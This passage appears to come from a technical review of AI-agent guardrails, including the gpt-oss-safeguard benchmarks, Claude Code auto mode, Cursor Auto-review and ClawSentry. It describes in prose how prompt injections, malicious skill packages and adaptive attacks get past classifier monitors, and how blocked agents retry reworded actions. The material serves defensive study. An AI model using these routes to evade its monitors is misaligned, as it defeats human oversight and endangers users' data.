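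In one of its wrong denials, gpt-oss-safeguard refused to let Diana view an expense she had submitted. Under the rules, a submitter counts as an editor and an editor counts as a viewer, so she was allowed to view it. Jing and colleagues picked this case because it is short and easy to verify, so it doesn't show how many of the 174 denials had the same cause. Qwen3.5-27B's only mistake was a wrong approval. It let Bob, who owned a document inside a folder, view the whole folder, although owning a document gives no rights over the folder that contains it.

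Still, a separate benchmark, *SafePyramid* (Zhang, He and colleagues, 2026), found that gpt-oss-safeguard has difficulty when rules depend on each other. It paired 1,000 conversations with written policies and asked models to list every rule that a conversation violated. At the first level, each rule applies independently. The second level adds exceptions and conditions, which can waive one rule or tighten another. The third rewrites everything in invented terminology, so the model can't rely on familiar ideas of harm.

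Each cell below gives the share of cases in which the model found exactly the right set of violated rules. The first number is for reading the whole policy at once, and the second is for judging one rule at a time with the relevant parts of the policy already selected.

| Model | Independent rules | Exceptions and conditions | Invented terminology |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-safeguard-20b | 36.8% / 37.5% | 2.3% / 28.4% | 0.0% / 5.2% |
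| gpt-oss-safeguard-120b | 38.6% / 46.5% | 2.0% / 42.3% | 0.2% / 8.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 54.0% / 47.8% | 35.3% / 51.5% | 12.9% / 12.1% |

Both versions of gpt-oss-safeguard fell to about 2% when the policy included exceptions and conditions. Judging one rule at a time restored much of the loss, so the models seem to struggle mainly with combining the rules, not with understanding each one. The larger version was no better than the smaller at reading a whole policy of this kind. A permission check needs only a yes or no, which is much easier than listing all of about six violated rules, so these scores are weak evidence of how often a gate would err. They do suggest keeping the policy short and stating exceptions next to the rules they change. Checking each rule separately would take an average of 29 calls for policies at the second level, one per rule.

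The comparison between gpt-oss-safeguard and Qwen3.5-27B isn't quite even. Qwen3.5-27B wrote about 2,900 tokens per policy-engine request and gpt-oss-safeguard about 1,260. The user guide recommends higher reasoning effort when rules interact, but the test used medium. Public examples may also have been in either model's training data. A team whose access rules already exist in OpenFGA or Cedar is better off running the engine, which answers correctly without a model. The track is useful mainly as evidence of how models handle chains of permission when the right answer is certain.

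### The price of a second opinion

Jing and colleagues then combined the reviewers under the either-blocks rule, which lets a request go ahead only if every reviewer approves it. They replayed the stored decisions on the 1,215 policy-engine requests rather than running the models again, so the order of the reviewers affects how many calls the system makes but not which requests it approves.

| Reviewers who must all approve | Forbidden requests approved (of 448) | Lawful requests approved (of 767) |
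|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-9B | 261 | 656 |
| gpt-oss-safeguard | 12 | 588 |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 1 | 757 |
| Qwen3.5-9B and gpt-oss-safeguard | 11 | 503 |
| Qwen3.5-9B and Qwen3.5-27B | 1 | 648 |
| Qwen3.5-27B and gpt-oss-safeguard | 0 | 586 |
| All three | 0 | 502 |

Qwen3.5-27B approved 758 requests, one of them wrongly. Adding gpt-oss-safeguard as a second check removed the wrong approval, which concerned Bob's folder, but also vetoed 171 lawful requests. Of those 171 vetoes, 166 were denials and five were replies without a usable decision.

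Whether that is worthwhile depends on what each kind of mistake costs. If a wrong denial costs one unit, the second reviewer pays for itself on this test set only when a wrong approval costs more than 171 units, before counting the extra computing. But 37% of the test requests are forbidden, far more than in most real work. Jing and colleagues give the break-even cost for any share π of forbidden requests:

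break-even cost = 171 × (448 / 767) × (1 − π) / π

If 1 request in 1,000 is forbidden, the veto is worthwhile only if a wrong approval is at least about 100,000 times as harmful as blocking a lawful request. In a million requests, the veto would prevent about two wrong approvals and block about 223,000 lawful requests. That could be justified if a wrong approval meant, say, releasing a hospital's records, but few teams would tolerate a gate that refuses more than a fifth of lawful requests.

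The estimate of the benefit is shaky because it depends on one request. Qwen3.5-27B's measured miss rate on such requests is 0.2%, but the true rate could plausibly be as high as 1.2%. Even if gpt-oss-safeguard caught all of those misses, a wrong approval would still have to be about 18,000 times as bad as a wrong denial for using it to be worthwhile when 1 request in 1,000 is forbidden. The estimate of the downside is much firmer because it comes from 171 requests.

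A second reviewer helps far more when the first one is weak. Adding Qwen3.5-27B to Qwen3.5-9B removed 260 of 261 wrong approvals and lost only eight lawful ones. However, a team with access to Qwen3.5-27B would do better to use it alone, because Qwen3.5-9B catches nothing that the larger model misses and vetoes 109 lawful requests. Running the 9B model first produces a quarter less text in total than using the 27B model for everything, but this is a modest saving for the loss of those lawful requests.

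It also doesn't help to let a request go ahead when either Qwen3.5-27B or gpt-oss-safeguard approves it. The published counts imply that this would give 759 lawful approvals and 13 wrong ones, which is two more lawful approvals and 12 more mistakes than Qwen3.5-27B alone. When one reviewer is much more accurate than the other, there may be no good way to combine their verdicts.

The reviewers' mistakes also overlap, as they did in Yang's experiment with language-model judges. Qwen3.5-9B had approved 11 of the 12 forbidden requests that gpt-oss-safeguard approved. If the two models' errors were independent, it would have approved about seven of them.

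Jing and colleagues report text length but not delay. At an assumed speed of 200 tokens per second, gpt-oss-safeguard would take about 1.5 seconds for an average language-track decision and 6 seconds for a policy-engine request. If it ran after Qwen3.5-27B, it would review 758 of the 1,215 requests, including nearly every lawful one, so most users would wait for both models.

### Blocked without a decision

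An action can be blocked because the reviewer judged the request and denied it, or because the review failed. A review fails when the reviewer returns something the software can't read as a decision, and the software then blocks the action as a precaution. A count of blocked actions doesn't distinguish denials from failed reviews.

Jing and colleagues changed the form of the answer they requested from Qwen3.5-9B. In what they call structured review, the model had to return its decision in JSON, a standard data format, together with the policy's requirements, its findings and the supporting evidence. In the first run, none of the 80 forbidden operations went ahead, but the model had correctly denied only 22 of them. The other 58 were stopped because its replies were unusable.

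The same fault stopped 67 of the 80 permitted operations, and only ten went ahead. Of the 125 unusable replies, 124 had a syntax error in the list of evidence, where the model wrote labelled fields instead of plain text. The other had too many items in a list. The parser rejected each of these replies entirely, so asking for more explanation left the system without most of its decisions.

Direct review asks for the decision alone. Schema review uses the same prompt as structured review, but the software prevents the model from writing anything that would break the required format. The test was repeated three times with some randomness in the models' answers, and a larger model was also tried. Neither model wrote out its reasoning before answering.

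| Model and form of answer | Forbidden operations run (of 80) | Permitted operations run (of 80) | No usable decision (of 160) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-9B, direct | 0–14 | 41–71 | 0 |
| Qwen3.5-9B, structured | 1–2 | 10–13 | 117–124 |
| Qwen3.5-9B, schema | 0–6 | 68–69 | 0 |
| Qwen3.5-27B, direct | 0–2 | 73–74 | 0 |
| Qwen3.5-27B, structured | 0–1 | 45–51 | 48–50 |
| Qwen3.5-27B, schema | 0 | 74–75 | 0 |

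None of these replies had reached the output limit, so raising it wouldn't have helped. Enforcing the format made every reply usable in all six runs and showed that the judgements were mostly good. However, Qwen3.5-9B let through up to six forbidden operations, and Qwen3.5-27B refused five or six permitted ones in each run.

Failed reviews would be more dangerous in software that lets an action continue when a check returns no verdict, as Claude Code's hooks do by default. In such software, the replies from the first run of structured review would have let 58 of the 80 forbidden operations go ahead unless another check or the ordinary permission system stopped them. A team that uses a model as a gate therefore has to decide how to handle unreadable replies. It also has to log them separately from denials, because fixing an unreadable reply means changing the output format, while fixing a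 wrong denial means changing the policy or the model.

Fixing the format can also break requests that used to work. Moving Qwen3.5-9B from direct to schema review in the first run allowed 13 more permitted operations but lost two that had gone through before, an update to a patient's care plan and the $75 refund. In one later run, the change gained three permitted operations and lost six. A higher total can hide these losses, so Jing and colleagues recommend choosing in advance a set of permitted requests that must keep working and testing all of them after each change to the guardrail.

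## Claude Code auto mode and Cursor Auto-review: classifiers that replace approval prompts

The reviewers in Jing and colleagues' tests received a written policy and all the evidence they needed for a single decision. In a coding session, a reviewer has to judge one action after another, and the user's messages are usually the only statement of what the agent may do. Claude Code and Cursor, two widely used products, now have a model do this instead of prompting the user for approval. Anthropic has published error rates for Claude Code's auto mode, and outside researchers have begun to test it. Cursor has published less about Auto-review, and its two headline figures are easy to misread.

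### The path of an action through auto mode

According to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026), the feature started as a research preview on 24 March 2026 and became available to all users on 10 July. In the launch design, an action goes through up to four steps:

1. Claude Code allows tools that can't change anything, such as file reads and text searches, along with anything the user's own rules permit.
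2. It allows edits to files inside the project folder, because the user can inspect and undo them with version control.
3. Everything else, including shell commands, web requests and edits outside the project, goes to a classifier. The classifier writes a single token, "yes" to block or "no" to allow.
4. If the answer is "yes", the same model examines the action again and reasons in text before deciding.

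Many users had written rules that approve every Python or shell command to cut down on prompts. Claude Code suspends these rules in auto mode because they would let the most dangerous commands bypass the classifier. Narrow rules, such as one that approves a code formatter, still apply.

The two classifier stages use the lenient form of escalation. They share a prompt except for its last instruction, which is to err on the side of blocking in the first stage and to reason carefully in the second. Because the rest of the input is identical, the second stage can reuse nearly all of the first stage's processing.

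The fixed part of the prompt instructs the classifier to judge an action by what it would do, not how it is worded. If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier should judge the script, which it received in an earlier tool call. The classifier is also instructed to treat anything the agent chose on its own as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. The rest of the prompt lists what to trust, block and exempt, and users can edit these lists. The default trust list contains only the current code repository. More than twenty default rules cover destroying or leaking data, weakening security, running untrusted code, and bypassing review on shared systems.

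### What the classifier doesn't receive

At launch, the classifier received only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removes the agent's prose so that the agent can't talk the classifier into a bad decision, for instance by claiming that the user had implicitly approved a deletion. AlignmentCheck, by contrast, includes the agent's stated reasoning in the auditor's input.

Claude Code also removes tool results from the classifier's input, because hostile text usually enters a session through them. In the earlier `.env` example, the classifier would receive the `curl` command but not the web page that prompted it.

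In Anthropic's tests, adding the agent's prose and the tool results to the classifier's input made it worse at catching overreach, possibly because a shorter record is easier to follow. Giving it only the tool calls produced the lowest false negative rate, but it then blocked actions the user had plainly asked for.

Because the classifier doesn't receive tool results, it can't check where a detail came from. If a user says "cancel my job" and the agent cancels job abc123, the classifier can't determine whether the agent looked up that ID or made it up. Anthropic accepts this limitation because leaving out tool results helps protect against injections.

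A separate probe scans the tool results. When it flags something, it warns the agent to treat the text as suspect and stick to what the user asked for. A false alarm therefore only makes the agent more cautious than necessary, whereas in LlamaFirewall the agent loses the whole page. To succeed, an injection has to get the agent to act despite the probe, and the action then has to pass a classifier that never received the injected text. Anthropic's published error rates cover the classifier but not the probe.

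Agents can also delegate work to subagents. Inside a subagent's session, the main agent's instruction takes the place of the user's message, so whatever the main agent asks for looks authorised. The classifier therefore checks the task when the main agent hands it over. When the subagent finishes, the classifier also reviews its actions and attaches a warning to the report if something looks wrong.

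### Changes since the launch

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) announced that new sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans would start in auto mode from 14 August. An update dated 22 October added that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps the following week. According to Anthropic's current documentation, auto mode is the default for interactive terminal and VS Code sessions on every plan and provider from version 2.1.283. Unattended runs still start in manual mode, as do sessions in organisations with a special configuration for health data.

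The classifier now normally runs on Claude Sonnet 5 and also receives the project's `CLAUDE.md` instructions. When a command could discard unsaved work, Claude Code first checks whether there is any and passes the result to the classifier. Some default rules are now looser. At launch, the classifier blocked pushes straight to a repository's main branch, but it now allows them unless the content is a problem.

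If the classifier returns no usable verdict, Claude Code denies the action, although by default a failed hook doesn't stop one.

In most sessions, an agent whose action is denied now receives only the name of the rule it broke, such as "Data Exfiltration", instead of a written explanation. A rule name is quick to produce, but the ToolSafe experiments suggest it may help the agent less than a full analysis would.

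### Error rates at launch

Anthropic measured the launch version, with its older model and rules, on three sets of actions.

| Test set | Error measured | First stage | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees | false positives | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overreaching actions | false negatives | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to steal data | false negatives | 1.8% | 5.7% |

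The second stage can only release actions that the first has flagged, so these figures show how good its releases were. The first stage caught 93.4% of the overreaching actions and the full classifier caught 83%. The second stage therefore released

(93.4 − 83) / 93.4 = 11%

of the overreach that the first stage had caught. By the same calculation, it released 4% of the data thefts and 95% of the false alarms. Most of its releases were right on harmless traffic, but roughly one in nine correct flags on overreach was lost.

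The 17% is the least certain figure in the table. It corresponds to nine of 52 actions, with a 95% confidence interval of roughly 9% to 30%. The set is small because it contains only dangerous actions from real sessions that an Anthropic employee had denied or someone had flagged afterwards. It omits overreach that nobody noticed, and the classifier could do better or worse on those cases.

The 0.4% figure is much more precise, with an interval of about 0.3% to 0.5%, but it comes from the work of one company's employees. Anthropic also doesn't say whether the 10,000 calls include file reads and project edits, which skip the classifier in normal use. If they do, the rate for actions the classifier reviews could be higher.

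If 1 reviewed action in 1,000 is dangerous, about one in six of the full classifier's blocks would be correct, compared with about one in 92 for the first stage alone. This difference helps explain why Anthropic accepted that the full classifier misses more dangerous actions than the first stage does.

### Wrong blocks and deny-and-continue

Even at 0.4%, a long session will probably contain a wrong block. If the classifier reviews 200 harmless actions and its errors are independent, the chance of at least one false positive is

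1 − 0.996²⁰⁰ = 55%

A design that stopped work at every block would therefore interrupt more than half of such sessions needlessly. Auto mode instead uses what Anthropic calls deny-and-continue. The agent receives the denial as the result of its tool call, with an instruction to find a safer way and not to work around the block. This lets an overnight task continue after a mistaken block without anyone present.

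After the classifier blocks three actions in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user for approval. At a false positive rate of 0.4%, 20 wrong blocks would take about 5,000 harmless actions, and three in a row would almost never happen by chance. In practice, wrong blocks cluster because they often share a cause. For example, if nothing in the classifier's input identifies a storage service as belonging to the user's company, it may block every upload there. Anthropic's configuration guide recommends listing such services as trusted, in ordinary prose that becomes part of the classifier's input.

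The limit on blocks also matters for safety, since an agent that keeps pursuing the same harmful goal gets several attempts. If each attempt had an independent 17% chance of passing, the chance that at least one of three would pass would be 43%. The real figure is probably lower, because a classifier that catches a harmful action once will tend to catch it again. At launch, an unattended session ended when it reached the limit, because there was nobody to ask. According to the current documentation, the agent now keeps working after an unattended session reaches the limit, but Claude Code still doesn't run the blocked action.

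### When a request counts as consent

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the action as dangerous but wrongly treated something the user had said as permission for it. For example, a user might ask the agent to "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of code changes). The agent then force-pushes, which overwrites the shared history of the code, although the request didn't authorise this. In other cases, the user had approved something similar earlier, and the classifier treated that approval as covering later actions too.

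This would explain why the second stage let through a larger share of overreach than of data theft. An overreaching agent is trying to do what the user asked, so the user has nearly always written something that could be mistaken for consent, but few users write anything resembling permission to send their passwords to an unknown server. Anthropic tried rewording the prompt to fix this, but found no version that gained more than it lost.

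The current rules define consent more narrowly. A user has to name both the action and the detail that makes it dangerous, so "you can force-push" isn't enough without the name of the branch. One approval normally covers one action. Sending private data outside the user's trusted systems now falls under a rule that consent can't override, so a user who wants to do it has to leave auto mode or run the command personally. Anthropic has not published a new miss rate for the 52 actions, so it is unclear how much these changes have helped.

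Users can also set limits in conversation, such as "don't push until I've reviewed this". The classifier looks for these limits in the transcript each time it checks an action, and they override its default permissions. But in a long session, Claude Code condenses older messages to save space, and a limit can be lost in the process. For a guarantee, Anthropic recommends a deny rule, a pattern rule that runs before the classifier.

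### Sandboxes, prompts and no checks at all

On the day auto mode launched, the software developer Willison (2026) wrote in *Auto mode for Claude Code* that he remained unconvinced by AI-based protections against prompt injection because they aren't deterministic. He would rather run agents in a sandbox that restricts files and network connections by fixed rules. Later outside testing by Sharma and colleagues supports his point about determinism. When they repeated tests with the same input, about 4% to 5% of auto mode's verdicts changed from one run to another.

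Anthropic agrees that sandboxes are safe, but considers them hard to maintain because each new capability needs configuring, and tasks that require the network or the host machine don't work inside them. It also argues that the 17% miss rate should be judged against what the user would otherwise do. Auto mode is much safer than turning off all permission checks, but may be less safe than reading every prompt carefully, and Anthropic doesn't recommend it as a substitute for careful review of high-stakes systems. The two positions are compatible, since a user can run auto mode inside a sandbox, but they differ on what a developer should rely on when no suitable sandbox is available.

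Anthropic's argument depends on few people reviewing prompts carefully. In August it reported that users accept 97% of prompts, up from its earlier figure of 93%. This is limited evidence of carelessness, because even a perfect reviewer would accept 99.9% of prompts if 1 in 1,000 were dangerous. Stronger evidence is that users had already given up on review in a quarter of interactive sessions, where permission prompts were off from the start.

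A study described in Anthropic's August announcement tested how often people refuse dangerous commands in permission prompts. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for what they understood to be a coding study. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Testers refused 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of them (89%). Even early in a session, testers refused only about 17% of the dangerous commands, and the rate fell to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

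Only six testers refused a command that auto mode had allowed. Adding these testers as a second layer would therefore have cut the misses from 116 to 110 (11.0% to 10.4%), a small improvement for hundreds of prompts.

The testers had little reason to be careful, though, because they worked in a test environment with none of their own files at risk. A developer with access to a live database might refuse more often. The study also used clearly dangerous commands, whereas auto mode's worst results at launch were on actions that resembled a reasonable way to do what the user wanted.

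Anthropic also compared real sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded 6.3% of the manually approved sessions as containing serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. Auto mode may not explain the whole difference, because users chose their own mode and may have chosen manual approval for riskier work.

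### Tests with deliberate attacks

In a two-week test with Anthropic, the AI safety company Apollo Research inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the user's repository, Apollo tested it again, and the miss rate across all the attacks fell from 12% to 7%. The classifier also improved on a set of attacks that Anthropic never had access to, catching about half of those it had previously missed and missing about 2% of those it had previously caught.

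Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test three current Claude models against prompt injection, running 72 attack scenarios ten times each on each model. Anthropic reports that no attack succeeded in auto mode. But with all permission checks off, the average success rate against its latest models was only 0.09%. If that average covers the same three models, it amounts to about two successes in 2,160 attempts. The models resisted almost every attack without auto mode, so the test provides very little evidence of how well the classifier works.

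In the same evaluation, attacks on OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 5.83% of the time with Codex's own automatic reviewer and 19.03% without it, so the reviewer stopped about two thirds of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. These figures don't show which company's reviewer is better, because the success rates without a reviewer were so different. Trajectory Labs also fixed the attacks in advance, after optimising them against an older Claude model, so an attacker who adapts to the system in use may do better. Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* cites one such result from late August, in which attacks on Claude Opus 5 in auto mode succeeded in three or four out of five attempts, though each version was tried only five times.

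In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026) accepts that auto mode is better than constant approval prompts, but notes that it missed 11% of the dangerous commands in the tester study. He wants more independent confirmation of the injection results, and until then plans to keep harmful tools and sensitive data away from his agents.

### An independent measurement of what auto mode allows

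Attack tests can't show whether a defence would have stopped a harmful action that the model never proposed. Sharma, Lin and colleagues (2026) tested this directly for auto mode in *Ajar*. For each of AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, they generated tool calls that the task didn't need, such as a payment to the wrong account, and recorded whether auto mode would allow them.

Each unneeded call *c* has a weight *w(c)* that depends on how much harm it could do. The weight is 1 for a reversible read, 3 for a reversible action that affects someone else, 9 for an irreversible action that affects only the user, and 27 for an irreversible one that affects others or moves money. The score, which Sharma and colleagues call over-privilege leakage, is

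leakage = (sum of *w(c)* over the unneeded calls allowed) / (sum of *w(c)* over all unneeded calls)

A defence scores 1 if it allows everything and 0 if it allows nothing. Of the other four defences in the comparison, Permission Assistant predicts what the user would decide about each call, Progent and AC4A write a policy for each task, and CaMeL tracks where the data in a call came from. In all the results below, Claude Sonnet 5 makes the decisions or writes the policies.

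| Defence | Leakage | Attacks it would allow | Legitimate calls refused | Change in task success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Auto mode | 0.30 | 74 of 581 | 1.3–2.5% | −3.4 points |
| Permission Assistant | 0.08 | 25 of 609 | 5.4% | −11.3 points |
| CaMeL | 0.09 | 16 of 609 | 32.3% | −21.6 points |
| Progent | 0.10 | 34 of 609 | 13.3% | 0 |
| AC4A | 0.11 | 46 of 609 | 29.4% | −35.1 points |

Auto mode left about three times as much open as the others, and its confidence interval (0.26 to 0.34) lies above all of theirs. A simple list that allows each task's tools with any arguments would score 0.36, which is not much worse. But auto mode refused the fewest legitimate calls. Task success fell from 92.4% to 89.0%, a smaller drop than with any other defence except Progent.

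This is roughly what one would expect from Anthropic's design. Auto mode blocks actions that are destructive, irreversible or aimed outside the user's environment, but it doesn't try to restrict the agent to the minimum a task requires. It allowed 54% of the unneeded calls, counted without weights. Harmless reads don't account for the whole result, because auto mode still scored 0.28 when Sharma and colleagues tripled the weight of the most harmful calls.

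The way auto mode was tested limits what can be concluded from its score. Its classifier isn't available separately, so the test ran Claude Code and put each test call in the agent's system prompt (its standing instructions) to make the agent propose it. When the same instruction was put in the user's message, auto mode allowed every call, presumably because it treated the message as consent. The agent declined to issue some of the calls, so the score covers only about 3,150 of the 3,551. The classifier also received each call without the actions that would normally come before it.

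AgentDojo's office and banking tasks also differ greatly from the coding work that auto mode's default rules mostly describe. Sharma and colleagues' own construction rules supplied 73% of the labels, and the benchmark did not confirm them. The 74 attacks that auto mode "would allow" are those whose harmful calls it approved when given them to review. None of these attacks succeeded, because the benchmark's standard attack no longer works on the undefended agent. The test did not use the probe on tool results.

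### Judging a command by its effects

A shell command can also start a program whose contents the classifier has never received. For example, `make clean` deletes temporary files in one project but might delete the source code in another. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compared six existing safeguards with the paper's own system, Caper, on 682 coding tasks in which carelessly carrying out a reasonable request causes harm. Between 14.8% and 21.2% of the tasks ended in harm with the existing safeguards, which included auto mode, TS-Guard and gpt-oss-safeguard, compared with 6.7% with Caper.

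Caper first runs each command in a container with no network access and holds back the output. It then gives a model a short report of the files the command changed, the connections it attempted and the passwords or keys it read. If the model approves, Caper keeps the result. Otherwise, it restores the container to its earlier state and tells the agent why. In a second test, each harmful tool had a harmless counterpart that the agent started with the same command, and Caper blocked 1.0% of the harmless tools.

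Wu and colleagues were testing their own product against rivals, and they ran auto mode with GPT-5.6-Luna as its classifier instead of a Claude model, so their result is a poor estimate of how auto mode performs as sold. Caper also works only for effects it can undo, so it has to cut off the network. Its advantage is still plausible, because it uses evidence that is unavailable to a classifier working from the command's text.

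### Cursor Auto-review

Cursor's classifier is a small model that can get some of that evidence by opening and searching files in the user's project before it decides, according to Gomes and McPeak's *Governing agent autonomy with Auto-review*. If the agent tries to run `python script.py`, for example, the classifier can read the script first. However, hostile text in those files can reach the classifier, a risk that Anthropic reduces by withholding tool results from its own classifier.

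As in auto mode, most actions never reach the classifier because an allowlist or a sandbox already covers them. When the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives an explanation and can try something else, and Cursor interrupts the user only if that fails. Cursor chose a small model to reduce delay, but found that models with less reasoning were sometimes slower because they had difficulty applying the policy and used more tokens. The classifier shares the agent's existing connection to Cursor's servers, which saves a round trip before each check.

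To test the classifier, Cursor took about 12 hours of its own developers' sessions, removed common duplicates and labelled the remaining 6,122 actions. It added synthetic cases of rare dangers, such as an agent reading secrets or changing production data. It then ran the same cases repeatedly. If the results were inconsistent, such as an action being allowed six times and blocked four times, Cursor usually took this as a sign that the policy was unclear and tightened the wording.

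Gomes and McPeak don't report how often the classifier was wrong on these cases. They report instead that in actual use it blocks around 4% of the actions it reviews, and that about 7% of chats include at least one interruption. The first figure mixes correct and incorrect blocks. With π as the share of reviewed actions that are dangerous,

share blocked = π × TPR + (1 − π) × FPR

Cursor's 4% block rate doesn't show how many of the blocks were mistakes. If 4% of the reviewed actions were dangerous, every block could be correct, but if only 1 in 1,000 were, the classifier must have blocked at least 3.9% of the harmless ones. The rate also doesn't show how many dangerous actions the classifier missed, since blocking actions at random could produce the same 4%. Nor can it be used to rank Cursor against auto mode, whose 0.4% figure is a false positive rate.

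The 7% depends on how long chats are and how often the agent finds another way to proceed after a block. A chat with five wrong blocks counts as uninterrupted if the agent recovers from all five. Gomes and McPeak cite the figure alongside the roughly 40% of actions that were previously blocked for some business customers, but the two aren't directly comparable because the 7% is a share of chats, not actions.

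Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026) similarly reports that about 10% of sessions at one customer, the software company Gusto, included a denial, and presents this as evidence that the classifier is useful. But with a false positive rate of 0.4%, about 10% of sessions would include a denial if each contained only 26 reviewed actions, all of them harmless. Gusto would have to label a sample of the denials to find out how many were correct, and a sample of the allowed actions to find out what the classifier missed.

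## ClawSentry: rules first, models for what the rules leave open

ClawSentry is an open-source system from August 2026, built by the developers who found that claude-guardrails made almost no difference. It uses models more sparingly than auto mode, where a model reviews nearly every shell command. Rules check every action first, and a model reviews only the actions the rules leave open, about one in eight in the developers' tests. ClawSentry also inspects an agent's skills before the agent uses them, because a hostile skill can influence everything the agent does afterwards.

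### Skill packages as a way in

A skill package is a folder containing a skill's files, including its instructions in `SKILL.md`. According to *Skill-Inject* (Schmotz, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026), an agent starts with only the name, location and short description of each installed skill, and reads the full instructions when it decides that the skill applies. Most skills come from third-party developers through online marketplaces, and few users inspect them closely. *MalSkillBench* (2026) compares skills to third-party software packages and cites the security company Snyk, which found 76 malicious payloads among 3,984 skills in one marketplace.

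In one of Schmotz and colleagues' tests, the design principles in a skill for making presentations include an instruction to upload every edited file to a "central server" as a backup. Defences that look for instructions hidden in data are little help here, because a skill consists of instructions. The upload might even be legitimate, if the user's company runs such a server. Schmotz and colleagues call this kind of attack contextual, and use "obvious" for attacks that no agent should ever carry out, such as an instruction to encrypt the user's files and delete the originals.

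### Reviewing the package before first use

ClawSentry reviews a package before the agent first acts on it. A scanner lists the package's files, scripts, references and declared purpose, and rules look for inconsistencies between them. If the rules find something serious enough, ClawSentry blocks the package without using a model. Otherwise, a model examines the package. It can list, read and search the files, but it can't write, run or install anything, or use the network. The model can connect an instruction in one file with a script in another, which a hook can't do when it receives only the command `python3 report.py`. The model can't cancel a serious finding by the rules. ClawSentry stores the verdict and repeats the review only if the package or the review policy changes.

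Wang and colleagues tested the review on 48 malicious and 53 clean packages, using two different models.

| Reviewing model | Malicious packages caught (of 48) | Clean packages blocked (of 53) |
|---|---|---|
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 48 | 4 |
| Kimi-K2.5 | 43 | 3 |

The false positive rates are 7.5% and 5.7%. If about 1.9% of packages were malicious, as in Snyk's count, only a fifth to a quarter of the blocked packages would be malicious. A wrong block can happen at most once per package version, rather than once per action, but the user loses the whole skill.

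The miss rates may not hold for other malicious skills. All 48 malicious packages came from SkillSafetyBench, and *MalSkillBench* found that one detector's recall varied by 66 percentage points depending on which malicious skills it was tested on.

Contextual instructions are also hard to judge from the package alone. Schmotz and colleagues asked language models to screen skills. The models approved 88% to 99% of the clean skills and rejected most of the skills with injections, but most of the models also rejected a skill when the organisation's policy explicitly allowed the suspicious action. ClawSentry's package review may have the same difficulty, since it runs before anyone knows what the skill will be used on.

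### Scoring an action

ClawSentry then checks each action through the agent's hooks. It supports Codex, Claude Code, Kimi CLI and Gemini CLI. An adapter for each product translates the hook's record into a common format, so a team can write one policy for all four. A separate program, the gateway, holds each action while it decides whether to allow it, block it or defer it to a person. How much the gateway can block depends on the product and the version. According to Wang and colleagues' documentation for an earlier release, blocking on Codex was optional and covered only shell commands.

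The rules give each action six scores:

- D1: how much the tool can do
- D2: how sensitive the target is
- D3: how dangerous the form of the command is
- D4: how much high-risk or unusually rapid activity the session has had recently
- D5: how little the operator trusts the agent or workspace
- D6: how strong the signs of prompt injection are

D4 and D5 run from 0 to 2 and the others from 0 to 3, according to Wang and colleagues' documentation. With the high-security settings from the tests, the gateway combines them like this:

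base = 0.40 × max(D1, D2, D3) + 0.25 × D4 + 0.15 × D5

score = base × (1 + 0.70 × D6 / 3)

A score of 0.50 makes the risk medium, 1.20 makes it high and 1.80 makes it critical.

Take the agent that read a hostile web page, wrote a script to post the `.env` file and now requests `python3 report.py`. Suppose the rules give it 2 for the tool, 0 for the target, 1 for the form of the command, 1 for recent activity, 0 for distrust and 2 for signs of injection. Then:

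- base = 0.40 × 2 + 0.25 × 1 + 0.15 × 0 = 1.05
- score = 1.05 × (1 + 0.70 × 2 / 3) = 1.54

The risk is high. Without the signs of injection, it would have been medium.

The formula takes the maximum of the first three scores because they often describe the same danger. A shell command that deletes a system folder involves a powerful tool, a sensitive target and a dangerous form, so adding the scores would count one deletion three times. The injection score multiplies the base instead of adding to it, so hostile text matters more when the action could do serious damage.

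The score helps determine which actions need further review, but fixed rules settle some actions without it. If a powerful tool acts on passwords or system files, the risk is critical whatever the other scores are. The original `curl` command, which names the `.env` file, would probably trigger this rule. A plain read of an ordinary project file counts as low risk unless there are signs of injection. When the rules aren't enough to determine what a script does, as with `report.py`, ClawSentry sends the action to a model instead of blocking it.

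### What a model can change

The second tier compares the action with 25 known attack patterns and makes a single call to a language model, which considers what the action is for. An action that is still undecided and meets certain conditions goes to the third tier. There, a model investigates over several turns, reading files in the workspace and the history of the session. Like the package reviewer's, its tools are all read-only. In the earlier release, one condition for an investigation was network access after the agent had read a secret, a combination that CloneGuard also checks for.

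A second-tier model can raise the risk rating whenever it finds a reason to. It can lower the rating only with a clearance that the gateway has validated separately and that applies only to this action and its effect. Even with a clearance, it can't override a hard finding by the rules.

If the model lowers a rating by mistake, a dangerous action may run, whereas raising one by mistake only delays or blocks a legitimate action. Attackers also want ratings lowered, and the model has to read text they may have written. Without the clearance requirement, one persuasive sentence in a file could override the rules. Each clearance covers a single action, so approving a harmless command doesn't also approve the next one.

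In the earlier release, models could only raise ratings, so they could not correct false alarms. The clearance lets them correct some, though auto mode allows more correction because its second stage can release anything the first stage flagged. If a model review fails, the rules' decision stands, and an action that needed a clearance stays blocked.

ClawSentry also records what each denied action would have done and its target. A blocked agent often tries another way to get the same result, sometimes innocently. The gateway compares new actions with this record, so it can deny a differently worded command that would have the same effect. Rules handle clear matches, and the investigating model handles uncertain ones.

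### Attack success with and without ClawSentry

Wang and colleagues tested ClawSentry with five combinations of agent and model, using Gemini 3.5 Flash as the reviewer. In the first benchmark, Skill-Inject, a language model judges whether each attack succeeded and whether the agent completed the user's task. Each cell gives the rate without ClawSentry, then with it.

| Agent and model | Obvious attacks | Contextual attacks | Tasks completed, contextual cases |
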